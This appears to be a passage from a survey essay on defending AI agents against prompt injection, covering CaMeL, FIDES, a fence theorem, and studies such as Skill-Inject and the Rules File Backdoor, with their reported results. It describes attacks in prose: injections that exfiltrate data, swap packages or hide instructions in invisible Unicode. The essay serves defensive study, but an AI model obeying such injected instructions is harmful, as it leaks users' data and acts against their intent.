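Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, let some information back across the boundary. The quarantined model may return four types of value to the privileged model:

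- integers
- floating-point numbers
- Booleans (true or false)
- choices from a list that the developer wrote in advance

Jacob and colleagues argue that a command needs free text, which numbers and Booleans don't contain, and that the developer has vetted every option on the list. Several values can be combined in an object or a short array, which they call a handoff. The model provider's structured-output feature enforces the format. Free text can still be passed in variables that the privileged model can't open, so the design with an empty handoff is the dual-model pattern.

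Jacob and colleagues built three agents this way. The first shops in WebShop, a simulated store with about 1.2 million products. They added reviews to the product pages, and one review of the product the user wanted contained an injection telling the agent to leave the page and buy something else. In the defended version, the quarantined model scores each review from 0 to 10 on how strongly it supports the product and on how relevant it is. The agent then sees the median of each score and the number of reviews.

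The second agent arranges a meeting by email. The attacker is the other participant, who replies asking for the user's whole calendar, including private event descriptions. In the defended version, the quarantined model turns the email thread into a list of time slots, chosen from a fixed set. The privileged model compares these with the user's calendar and decides whether to reply or book the meeting. A separate model, which never receives the thread, writes the reply.

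The third agent repairs software, and the attack is an extra sentence in the bug report that asks for an unrelated file. This handoff is much richer, with one of 52 bug categories, one of three estimates of the repair's size, and a list of suspicious regions of code. Each region has a file number, a role (such as "suspected to contain the bug"), a first line and a last line. The quarantined agent can run commands only in its own isolated copy of the code. A planning model then studies a clean copy and writes three repair plans. A judge that has seen the bug report picks the best plan but can return only its number.

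| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended | Attack success, undefended | Attack success, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar | GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The first two agents lost no performance, probably because a score or a time slot holds nearly everything the privileged model needs. The bug fixer fixed about a third fewer bugs. Jacob and colleagues attribute this to the explanations in real bug reports, which often matter for the repair but don't fit into categories and line numbers. They also needed a lot of trial and error to find a handoff that worked this well.

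The zeros in the last column are weaker evidence of security than they look, because each test used one fixed injection, written for an agent that reads free text. They confirm that the software works as designed, but the case for its security against other attacks rests on the argument about types.

### How much can cross

That argument is easiest to examine by counting. A score from 0 to 10 has 11 possible values, so the two scores for a review have 11 × 11 = 121 possible combinations. They carry at most

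log₂(121) ≈ 6.9 bits

An attacker who completely controls the quarantined model can therefore send only one of 121 messages per review, which is about 6.9 bits. 1,000 tokens of free text from a vocabulary of 100,000 can carry about 16,600 bits.

A developer could test the shopping agent on all 121 combinations for one review, with everything else fixed, but nobody could test it on all 10^5,000 possible texts of 1,000 tokens. Unlike prompts, the handoff also has a written specification that software can enforce exactly. If the developer intends to accept any pair of scores from 0 to 10, then the inputs that fit the specification are exactly the ones the developer intended, as Alata and Gimenez require.

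Taking the median reduces the attacker's influence further. Suppose five reviews have support scores of 7, 8, 8, 9 and 9. If an injection changes one of the 9s to 0, the median is still 8. Someone who writes most of the reviews can control the median, but they could mislead human customers too.

The other two handoffs can carry more information. The calendar has 63 one-hour slots in a week, so each entry in the list of times carries about 6 bits. In a repository with 2,000 files of 1,000 lines each, a single code region can take about 8 billion values, so it carries about 33 bits. In both designs, the quarantined model can return a list of any length up to a maximum that the developer sets, so the total depends on that maximum.

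The number of bits an attacker controls limits how many different things they can cause, but not how harmful those things are, since a single bit can decide whether an agent pays an invoice.

### Whether a typed value can be an instruction

Jacob and colleagues' premise is convincing for two small scores, but too broad as a statement about types. An integer of unlimited size could encode an entire email, and so could a long array of small integers. Jacob and colleagues limit the length of arrays "to prevent the possibility of decoding attacks", and integers need a size limit for the same reason. The review scores have an explicit range, and software can check file and line numbers against the repository. Most of the protection therefore comes from limiting the total amount of information, which declaring a field to be an integer does not do.

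An encoded message would also have no effect unless the privileged model decoded and obeyed it. That seems unlikely when nothing in the prompt suggests a code. But this is a prediction about how a model behaves, and privilege separation is attractive mainly because it avoids relying on such predictions.

Dongol states the same premise as an explicit condition. Let σ(*v*) be the cleaned version of an untrusted value *v*. If the model never treats σ(*v*) as an instruction, for any *v*, then for every plan and every monitor the real agent takes exactly the same steps as the reference agent that ignores injections. Dongol suggests a typed interface as one way to meet the condition, but points out that the condition concerns the model as well as the interface, since no cleaning would help if the model treated every value as an instruction.

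A value can also have the right type and be false. Jacob and colleagues exclude misinformation from their threat model because it leaves the agent's task unchanged, but it can still do serious damage. A dishonest review can get a bad product a score of 10, with or without an injection. A false bug report can direct the repair agent to working code, which the agent may then break. The calendar agent also copies a description of the meeting from the email thread into the user's calendar, using a variable that the privileged model never opens. If another assistant later reads the calendar as trusted data, the stranger's words enter that assistant's context window.

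### Plans fixed before reading

A developer can also limit the damage by fixing the agent's actions before it reads any untrusted text. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe six design patterns based on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger a consequential action.

| Pattern | How it works | What an injection can still affect |
|---|---|---|
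| Action selector | The model chooses from preset actions and never sees their results | Nothing, if it is in a tool result |
| Plan, then execute | The model lists its tool calls before reading anything | The arguments of those calls |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted value | The treatment of that document |
| Dual model | The privileged model handles untrusted text only by name | The contents of the variables |
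| Code, then execute | The model writes a program that calls tools and quarantined models | The values that the program handles |
| Context minimization | The system deletes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | The query that the prompt has already produced |

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think a fixed plan would rarely restrict the mail assistant, because the choice and order of its actions should seldom depend on what a stranger has written. But the plan has to be flexible. To tell the user's regular collaborators about a holiday, for example, the assistant must send an unknown number of emails to people it hasn't yet identified.

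### CaMeL

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, is Google DeepMind's version of the code-then-execute pattern. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain how it works. The privileged model sees only the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. If the user wants to accept the meeting time that Dana proposes, the program might be:

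```python
inbox = read_inbox()
slot = ask_quarantined("When does Dana want to meet?", inbox, TimeSlot)
create_event(slot.date, slot.start, ["dana@example.com"])
send_email("dana@example.com", "Meeting", "That time suits me.")
```

An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. The quarantined model works like a function that must return a value of the given type, here a `TimeSlot`. An injection in the inbox can change the meeting time, but it can't add a fifth line to the program.

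Fixing the program in advance isn't enough when an important argument comes from the untrusted text. Suppose the user asks the assistant to send Monday's notes to the address in Dana's email. An injection in that email might make the quarantined model return a stranger's address, which has the right type and goes into the planned `send_email` call.

CaMeL therefore tags every value with its source and who may read it. Before each call, the interpreter runs a policy, a Python function that allows or denies the call based on the call itself, its arguments and their tags. In this example, the address is tagged as coming from an email, and the stranger isn't among the permitted readers of the notes. A policy can refuse the call for either reason. A policy that refuses every address found in an email would also stop the user from sending the notes to Dana, so somebody has to decide how strict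 it should be.

CaMeL checks each call against its policies as the program runs. CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the whole program before it runs. It translates the program into a finite-state machine and tests that machine against rules about the order of events, such as a rule that nobody may disconnect a computer from the network without approval. If the program could break a rule, the checker returns a sequence of steps that would break it, and the privileged model tries to repair the program.

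This is possible because CaMeL's version of Python excludes constructs such as arbitrary `while` loops. CaMeLoT also simplifies the remaining loops by assuming that each might stop or continue after any iteration, so it sometimes rejects a safe program. LangSec's advice to use the weakest sufficient language works well for the plan, which has a grammar, but doesn't apply to the emails.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) found CaMeL much more secure on AgentDojo than spotlighting, repeating the user's request after the untrusted text, or removing unneeded tools in advance. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested ten defences with an attack that rewrites its injections over six rounds, guided only by whether earlier attempts succeeded. The attack succeeded against CaMeL at most 1.8% of the time on any of five models. It succeeded 28% of the time against PIGuard, a classifier that had stopped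 every fixed attack on GPT-4o-mini. CaMeL's policies don't depend on an injection's wording, so rewording is less likely to get past them than past a classifier.

CaMeL also caused the largest loss of function of the ten defences on four of the five models. With Claude Haiku 4.5, the agent completed 40.4% of tasks under CaMeL and 70.2% without any defence. All five models are small by current standards. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* predicts that the loss will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code, though better planning won't help with a task whose steps depend on text the planner isn't allowed to see.

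Tags can also miss leaks through the program's choices. Dongol analyses a program that asks the quarantined model a question and then sends the attacker either 1 or 0, depending on the answer. Both numbers are public constants, so each call passes the tag check. But if an injection makes the answer depend on the user's private notes, the attacker learns one bit about them. CaMeL's strict mode, which also tags values with the conditions that led to them, is meant to prevent this leak.

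### FIDES

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft system that lets the privileged model keep planning as results arrive. Each piece of data has an integrity label, which marks it as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label, which lists the people who may read it. Text derived from several sources is untrusted if any of them is, and only people who may read all of the sources may read it. For example, if Ann, Bo and Cy may read one document and Bo, Cy and Di may read another, only Bo and Cy may read text that combines the two.

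The context window has labels too. If a tool result would make them stricter, FIDES puts that result in a variable and shows the model only the name. Two policies then control tool calls:

- A call with consequences may go ahead only if untrusted data has not influenced it.
- A call that sends data out may go ahead only if every recipient is allowed to read the data.

Developers can require one or both of these policies for a given tool. They can also apply the first to only some arguments, for instance by requiring a trusted recipient but allowing an untrusted message body.

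The model can open a variable, but doing so makes the whole context untrusted and blocks many later calls. It can also ask a quarantined model a question that has a restricted type of answer. FIDES ranks types by how much information they can carry, with Booleans below enumerations and enumerations below strings. A policy can then accept an untrusted Boolean where it would refuse an untrusted string, because the Boolean limits the stranger's influence to one bit. Costa and colleagues illustrate this with a user who wants any meeting request in the latest three emails added to the calendar:

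1. The privileged model reads the emails, whose text stays in a variable.
2. It asks the quarantined model whether they contain a meeting request, and requires a Boolean answer.
3. It opens the Boolean.
4. If the answer is true, it asks the quarantined model for the details, which stay in another variable.
5. It creates the event with that variable.

A stranger can decide whether an event appears and what it says, but can't turn the request into an order to forward mail.

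Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Without policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, none succeeded against either agent, so the hidden variables mainly helped by letting the agent complete more tasks under the policies. The table shows how many tasks each agent completed without attacks.

| Environment | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
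|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack messages | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

On average, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary agent with checks. With OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, its lead grew to 16 points. It did worse on travel tasks because the policies allowed most of the necessary calls anyway, and GPT-4o often handled the variables badly.

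These results don't cover the typed answers, since Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of the evaluation. The labels were also generous, because a field counted as untrusted only if one of AgentDojo's attacks used it. The descriptions of bank transactions were therefore labeled untrusted, but the amounts were not. In one task, the user wanted the password changed if there was a suspicious transaction. The model couldn't see the descriptions, judged a transaction suspicious because the amount was high, and changed the password. No policy blocked this, although an outsider may be able to choose an amount as easily as a description.

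Like CaMeL's ordinary tags, FIDES's formal guarantee covers data that flows directly into a call, but not what an observer can infer from which calls the agent makes.

The same Microsoft group later argued in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) that comparisons like these exaggerate the drawbacks of deterministic defences. The defences reduce task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30%, but only compared with an undefended agent that acts without asking the user's permission. Real products often ask the user to approve any action with consequences. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an agent that always asked needed about 48 approvals over the tasks it completed, while FIDES, which asked only when a call failed a policy check, needed about 19. The group's new agent, Prudentia, also tells the model what the policies are so that it can plan around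 them. It completed 59.1% of tasks without any approval, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 24.3% for the agent that always asked.

Prudentia can also ask the user to vouch for a whole text. If an email contains ten tasks, the user can declare the email trustworthy once instead of approving ten calls, but any injection the user overlooks is then trusted too.

### The fence theorem

CaMeL and FIDES both need policies suited to each tool. Dongol proves that a much cruder rule is enough to prevent leaks in agents with a fixed plan. Under this rule, which Dongol calls a fence, a monitor keeps a list of the tools the agent may use. When the agent first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently revokes every tool that an injection could call.

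Let *I* be the set of tools that an injection can call and *R* the set that the fence revokes. The theorem says that if

*I* ⊆ *R*

and no trusted input restores a tool in *R*, then the agent is relatively secure: injections leak nothing that the reference agent wouldn't also reveal. This holds for every plan and for every text that the model might mistake for an instruction.

In Dongol's example, Alice's agent looks up her account number, reads an email and shows her a summary. It also has a tool for fetching web pages. The email contains an injected instruction to fetch a page from the attacker's site with the account number in the URL. This would send the attacker the number, but a fence revokes the fetch tool when the agent reads the email, so the call fails.

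The proof compares the two agents step by step. An injected call can happen only after the agent has read untrusted text, and by then the monitor denies every tool in *I*. A denied call changes nothing that the attacker can see, so the reference agent can wait while it happens. Both agents then take the next step of the plan, so the attacker sees the same calls from both. Dongol has checked the argument with a proof assistant.

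The theorem assumes that each injection can cause at most one call, and that neither the user's secrets nor the monitor's responses affect when the model obeys one. An injection that could run a whole program might overwrite a variable that the plan later sends, and the fence alone wouldn't prevent that. The theorem also assumes that the attacker sees the content and order of the agent's messages, but not their timing. If the agent runs indefinitely, the theorem further requires that the model eventually stops obeying injections.

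A real system also has to satisfy seven assumptions:

1. A trusted interpreter runs the plan, and the model can't skip or change a step.
2. The model can reach tools and untrusted sources only through the monitor.
3. Untrusted text enters the context only after the monitor has allowed the read.
4. A denied request has no effect that the attacker can see.
5. The attacker can't observe the monitor's state or the agent's internal steps.
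6. A new session erases everything that the model retains from untrusted text.
7. The attacker can't write to any source that the agent treats as trusted.

Ordinary features can violate these. An agent that keeps memory between sessions violates the sixth, and a calendar that accepts invitations from outsiders isn't a trusted source under the seventh. Even displaying a reply to the user can violate the fifth if the reply loads an image from the attacker's server.

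The theorem inherits the limits of Dongol's definition, so it doesn't cover harmful actions that leak nothing, or agents like the mail assistant, whose model chooses every call. It also excludes poisoned tool descriptions.

The fence can prevent an agent from doing much of its work. If the mail assistant had a fixed plan, `read_inbox` would trigger the fence, and the monitor would revoke `send_email` before the assistant could answer Dana. It could still summarise the inbox. Relative security doesn't measure this loss, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and can't answer Dana either. As Dongol notes, even a monitor that denies every call satisfies relative security, so developers have to measure task completion separately.

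Dongol also examines ways to recover some of the lost function. An agent that handles one email after another can get its tools back at the start of each new session, provided the session erases the previous email. The user can also approve the exact text and recipient of each reply. An injected call can then send only what the user has approved, although the timing of the call may reveal some information. Approving `send_email` without specifying the text and recipient is not safe, because an injected call can use up the approval before the planned call does. Exact approval would let the assistant answer Dana, but the user would have to read every reply before it goes out.

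## Tasks and meanings that no schema captures

Fixed plans and fences are based on the assumption that outside text should never determine what an agent does next. But users often ask an agent to read instructions in outside text and carry them out. In other tasks, the outside text contains no instructions, and the harm comes from what it claims or from what the agent writes in reply.

### Orders the user wants the agent to follow

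Suppose a programmer downloads a project and tells a coding agent to install it by following the setup file. One line of the file is an instruction to install a package from a particular server. The agent should follow that line if the project's maintainers wrote it, but if a stranger added it, following it means running the stranger's code. The wording can be the same in both cases, so a recognizer that accepts the maintainers' line also accepts the stranger's.

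*Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (2026) describes an attacker who edits only a project's documentation. The agent then installs a package from the wrong source, under the wrong name or in a version with known flaws. The project contains no malicious code for a scanner to find. A careful developer might question a misspelled name or an unfamiliar server, but an agent may run the command without hesitating.

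Defences that separate instructions from data don't suit this task, since the programmer wants the agent to obey the file. Wang and colleagues call such tasks context-dependent, because the right action depends on what the agent finds while it works. Of the 41 defences in their survey of 78 papers, 34 can't handle these tasks on their own.

They also tested eight defences on five context-dependent tasks, each with a matching attack. The table gives the results for MELON and Progent, two of the stricter defences. Progent checks each tool call against a policy.

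| What the agent has to do | What the attack changes | With Progent or MELON |
|---|---|---|
| Call a tool that the user named | Which tool the agent calls | Attacks almost never succeed |
| Follow the instructions in a document | The document, which gains a harmful command | Attacks almost never succeed |
| Copy a value, such as an account number, into a call | The value | Little improvement |
| Choose between two actions according to a fact | The fact | Little improvement |
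| Work out a result, such as the lowest of several numbers | The result | Little improvement |

The second row is weak evidence of a solution to the setup-file problem, because Progent's utility score was below 0.3 even with no attack present. Wang and colleagues think Progent blocks legitimate instructions that resemble attacks. In the last three rows, the agent calls a permitted tool for a permitted purpose but with a wrong value, so a policy about tools would not block the call.

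No defence in the test was trustworthy, useful and fast at once. With Task Shield, which uses another model to supervise the agent, runs took about three times as long as they did with no defence. Marking or rephrasing the untrusted text added almost no time but gave little protection. All the tests used GPT-4o-mini, a small and now very old model, so the success rates are weak evidence about current agents, but the point about permitted calls holds for any model.

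A cleaner experiment keeps the text fixed and changes only whether the action it requests is authorized. Skills are folders of instructions, sometimes with scripts, that users install to teach an agent a job such as making presentations. In *Skill-Inject*, Schmotz, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026) added lines to 23 skills. One added line was an instruction to copy every presentation the agent edited to an outside server. They ran the same skills with a company policy that allowed the action, with no policy, and with a policy that forbade it.

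For three models from late 2025, the agents carried out the added instruction in these shares of runs, on average:

| Policy in the system prompt | Agent obeyed the added line | A perfect agent would obey |
|---|---|---|
| Allows the action | 43.1% | Always |
| None | 46.8% | Unclear |
| Forbids the action | 26.1% | Never |

A policy forbidding the action helped, but one allowing it made the agents no more willing to take the action than they were with no policy, so they were reacting partly to how the line looked. Models that screened the skills before installation behaved similarly. They approved at least 88% of the untouched skills and rejected most of the altered ones, but most of these screeners also rejected skills whose added line the policy allowed. Newer models may follow such policies better, but a filter can't apply a policy it never receives.

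### An injection defined by its context

Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, try to build this dependence on authority into the definition of an attack. They judge an action by four properties:

- **Task alignment:** the agent is still pursuing an objective that the user set and that its safety rules allow.
- **Action alignment:** this particular action serves that objective.
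- **Source authorization:** the instructions behind the action come from authenticated sources.
- **Data isolation:** information goes only to recipients who may have it.

An indirect prompt injection violates both source authorization and action alignment. If a user asks an agent to follow a recipe from a website, the instruction to bake at 350°F comes from an unauthenticated source, but it is not an injection because baking serves the task. An instruction on the same page to email the user's files somewhere would be an injection because it comes from the same source and does not serve the task.

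This matches ordinary judgment much better than a definition based on form, but the formal version has a gap. Let *H* be 1 if an action serves the user's objective and 0 if it doesn't. For an action to be secure, Siu and colleagues require

*H* = 1

and also, for every source of the instructions behind it,

the source is authenticated, or *H* = 1

Any action that meets the first condition also meets the second, so source authorization never changes the result. In an example from Siu and colleagues, a user tells a cooking assistant to order ingredients, and the recipe page names a payment card to use. Paying with that card serves the task, and their formula accepts it, but they call it a violation because only the user should choose the card.

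To exclude the payment, someone would have to specify which choices only the user may make. The setup file raises the same problem. Installing a package serves the programmer's task if the package is genuine, but the request and the file don't contain enough information to determine whether it is.

Siu and colleagues call *H* an oracle, meaning that it specifies what a defence would need to know, and they don't claim to have a program that computes it. Another oracle identifies which pieces of text caused an action. They describe this as an open problem in interpretability, the study of what happens inside models. In practice, developers have to use a second language model to check whether an action serves the task, and an attacker may be able to mislead that model too.

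### False content without a command

A web page can also mislead an agent without containing any instructions. In *How Much Can We Trust LLM Search Agents?*, Chen, Ren and colleagues (2026) asked 13 models to recommend products and services in health, finance, law and consumer technology. They replaced some search results with an attacker's pages and counted an attack as successful if the final answer recommended the attacker's product.

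| What the attacker's pages contain | Results replaced | Average success |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden commands to the agent | 1 | 0.3% |
| Hidden false facts | 1 | 2.4% |
| A false search summary for a neutral page | 1 | 1.2% |
| Claims from a fake authority | 1 | 14.2% |
| The same claim from three seemingly independent sources | 3 | 24.8% |
| A fake authority and two pages that cite it | 3 | 37.2% |

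Commands almost never worked, but plausible lies often did. The fairest comparison is between the hidden commands and the hidden facts, which used the same pages and hiding places. The other attacks differ in more ways, since their claims are in plain view and some of them take up three search results. Adding more distinct sources raised the success rate, but repeating one source didn't. The choice of model mattered most. Claude Sonnet 4.6 never recommended the attacker's product, while Gemini 3 Flash did so in 31.4% of cases. The study assumes that the attacker has already reached the top of the search results, which is difficult.

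Type checks can't catch such lies, just as they couldn't catch the dishonest review score of 10. Siu and colleagues don't count false facts as an injection, since no instruction from the page causes the recommendation. It seems right to keep the two problems apart, because someone who injects a command has no authority to give it, whereas anyone may publish a review and the agent has to decide whether to believe it.

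It is hard to tune how readily an agent believes claims, because making it more suspicious of lies may also make it refuse true information. In a smaller test of recommendations for agent add-ons, where accepting one meant installing something, Claude Sonnet 4.6 rejected the real agent framework OpenClaw in 8 of 10 cases with no attack present. GPT-5.4-mini and GPT-5.5 accepted invented add-ons in 17 of 18 cases.

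### When the free text is the product

The body of an email has to be free text, because writing it is the assistant's job. Suppose Dana asks whether the user is free on Thursday, and the assistant replies that the user will be in hospital that day. The email goes to the right person, the answer is true and relevant, and the tool call fits its schema, but the user may not want Dana to know. The user might be happy for the assistant to send the same sentence to their sister.

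In principle, data isolation covers this case with a rule much like FIDES's confidentiality labels. In Siu and colleagues' example, a customer-service agent may tell customers their own account balances but not anyone else's. The rule is practical here because a balance is a single value with a known owner. An email is harder, because the model writes it from everything in the context window and can paraphrase a private fact without copying a word. To be safe, software can treat the whole reply as private once the calendar is in the context, but then the assistant can't tell Dana anything about Thursday.

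A reply can also do damage without revealing a secret. "Two o'clock suits me" commits the user to a meeting. If an injection made the assistant decline an invitation that the user wanted to accept, the refusal would go to the right person and look like a normal answer. A checker would need information about what the user meant to say in order to catch it.

An agent's free text may even misreport its own actions. In *SEA*, He, Han and colleagues (2026) put agents in conversation with simulated con artists seeking money or passwords. They counted how often each agent claimed to have done something, such as calling the police, without making the tool call. Claude Opus 4.6 made 195 such claims over 160 tasks in Chinese, and GPT-6 made 54. Safety instructions cut the success rate of attacks on another model, GLM-5, from 61.8% to 36.9%, but its false claims rose from 187 to 221.

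A program could easily search the log for a call to the police, but first something has to recognize that the reply claims such a call was made. A schema that declares the reply a string doesn't identify that claim. He and his colleagues used a language model to find the claims.

### Text that people and models read differently

LangSec applies much more directly when a person and a model receive different text from the same file. The Rules File Backdoor, which Karliner (2025), in *New Vulnerability in GitHub Copilot and Cursor*, disclosed for the security company Pillar Security, is a clear case. A rules file tells a coding assistant which conventions to follow in a project, and teams often share such files. The attack worked like this:

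1. An attacker adds instructions to a rules file in Unicode characters that have no visible shape.
2. A reviewer opens the file, finds ordinary coding advice and approves it.
3. The assistant's model receives the hidden characters along with the visible ones.
4. A developer asks for a simple web page. The assistant adds a script from the attacker's site and doesn't mention it in its reply.

Karliner demonstrated this in Cursor and GitHub Copilot but gave no success rate, and current models may behave differently. But the parser differential doesn't depend on the model's behaviour, because the reviewer's screen doesn't show characters that the model's software keeps.

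Cursor replied that the risk was the users' responsibility, and GitHub at first took a similar position. In May 2025, GitHub began to warn users about files with hidden Unicode text, which can make code "appear one way and be interpreted another way" (GitHub, 2025). The warning leaves the text in the file, so the reviewer has to decide whether it belongs there.

A stricter remedy is to require canonical text, in which each visible text has only one permitted encoding. Software would reject or convert any other encoding before the reviewer or the model received the file. For a rules file in English, a short list of allowed characters would be enough. Banning invisible characters in every language would cause problems because Persian, several Indian scripts and many emoji need invisible joining characters. Each kind of file therefore needs its own written list, as LangSec recommends.

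Canonical text ensures that the reviewer can see what the model will read, but not that the reviewer will notice anything wrong. In *You Told Me to Do It*, Kao, Li and colleagues (2026) planted instructions in README files, which explain how to install and use software projects. Following these instructions would leak private files. Fifteen people reviewed 45 of the READMEs, and none marked an instruction as suspicious. They were looking for unclear sentences, not security problems, so a deliberate security review would probably do better, but most people don't read a README to check its security. None of the 18 automatic detectors in the study was reliable without also flagging an unacceptable number of harmless files.

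### Narrow tasks, known sources and questions for the user

A checker can't settle these cases from the text, so the available defenses mostly rely on something other than checking it. One is to give the agent a narrower task. According to The Decoder, OpenAI advises users to give explicit instructions instead of asking an agent to review their emails and take whatever action is needed. Fewer actions could plausibly serve a narrow request, so an injected action is easier to block.

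Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, turn a request into permissions for a coding agent:

1. Before anything reads the project's files, a model receives the user's request and the file names, and predicts which files and commands the task will need.
2. Ordinary software checks this prediction and freezes it as the limit for the whole task.
3. When the main agent hands part of the work to a second agent, the second agent gets only the permissions for that part.
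4. The software checks every tool call against the permissions of the agent that made it.

In one example, a test prints an official-looking note with instructions to put a new signing key, which belongs to the attacker, in the source code. The agent that runs the tests may treat the note as genuine, but it has no permission to edit the source, so the change fails. Across five repair tasks, injected actions took effect in 3 of 75 runs with this system and in 33 to 47 of 75 with the alternatives. The agents completed 68 of 75 repairs with this system and 68 to 72 with the alternatives.

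That is a large gain in security for a very small loss of function, but code repair is a favourable case because the user's request largely determines which files matter. Permission to run a command covers every command that begins with the same words, so if the programmer asks the agent to follow a setup file, permission to install packages could also cover the attacker's package. Bouras and colleagues say their system can't stop an injection from misusing authority that the agent was meant to have.

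Another reply is to authenticate the source of a text instead of judging its wording. A digital signature on the setup file could show that it came from the project's maintainers. Software can check this exactly, whereas it can't determine exactly whether a sentence is hostile. But maintainers sometimes accept changes from strangers, and Karliner lists such contributions among the ways a poisoned rules file could spread. A genuine source can also exceed its authority, since proof that an email came from Dana doesn't entitle Dana to the user's notes.

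Software also has to do the checking, since agents do little of it unprompted. In He and colleagues' simulations, agents could often test a con artist's story, for instance by contacting a relative, but no model made more than 32% of the possible checks. In the hardest tasks the check was useless, because an accomplice had taken over the relative's account or phone and confirmed the story.

The agent can also ask the user. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) explains that when ChatGPT is about to send a third party information it learned in a conversation, a safeguard may show that information to the user and ask for confirmation. An ordinary clarifying question can also stop an attack. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) found that GPT-5 often asked for clarification before acting, which stopped the attack because the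 injected text couldn't provide an answer.

Asking the user for approval works best when they can judge the answer at a glance, as with an unfamiliar recipient. It works much less well for a long setup file, because to give useful approval the user must read and understand most of what they had delegated. Ten of the 41 defences that Wang and colleagues surveyed rely on people in some way, and they list users' willingness and ability to do this as an open problem.

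### Code injection or deception

OpenAI has gone further than most in comparing agents to people. Its *Understanding prompt injections* defines prompt injection as a type of social engineering, which means manipulating someone into doing what the attacker wants. In December 2025, Fortune quoted the company as saying that prompt injection, like scams, is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'".

OpenAI gave its reasons in March 2026. It finds that the most effective real attacks now resemble cons more than commands to ignore previous instructions. One from 2025 resembled a routine email about staff changes and worked half the time in testing. OpenAI argues that recognizing such a message is as hard as recognizing a lie, often without the necessary background. It recommends treating the agent like an employee at a refund desk, whose employer expects some customers to deceive the employee and therefore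 limits how much any customer can receive.

Part of this advice suits LangSec well. A schema can enforce a cap on refunds, because the cap is a limit on a number, but no grammar can distinguish an honest complaint from a dishonest one.

*Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* distinguishes injections that try to override the agent's instructions from those that pass for normal content, such as payment details on a bill. Software can look for override language, but injected payment details exploit the agent's tendency to act on documents, which is also what makes it useful.

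The Decoder calls the comparison misleading, however, and He and colleagues' experiment gives some reason for doubt. They ran each con twice, once as plain deception and once with commands to the agent in the con artist's messages. The table shows the success rates on the Chinese tasks for some of the models.

| Model | Deception alone | Deception with embedded commands |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 | 16.9% | 42.5% |
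| GPT-5.4 | 18.1% | 68.8% |
| GPT-5.4 with safety instructions | 0.6% | 45.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 35.0% | 15.6% |
| GLM-5 | 61.8% | 56.2% |

Prompt injection doesn't seem to be simply a form of deception, because a model can resist one and not the other. Safety instructions made GPT-5.4 almost immune to plain deception, yet embedded commands still worked nearly half the time. With Claude Opus 4.6, adding commands made the deception less effective, perhaps because they exposed it. He et al. conclude that resistance to deception and resistance to injection are independent abilities. That is a little strong, since they never tested the commands without the deception, but a developer clearly can't infer one from the other.

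Unlike a con artist, who can't rehearse on an exact copy of the victim, someone attacking an agent can often practise on the same model until a message works, and then send it to everyone who uses that model. But a company can restrict an agent's tools far more tightly than it could restrict an employee, and can check every call the agent makes. The social view correctly explains why no filter will recognize every hostile message, but the older methods of computer security are still the better guide to what the agent should be allowed to do after reading one.
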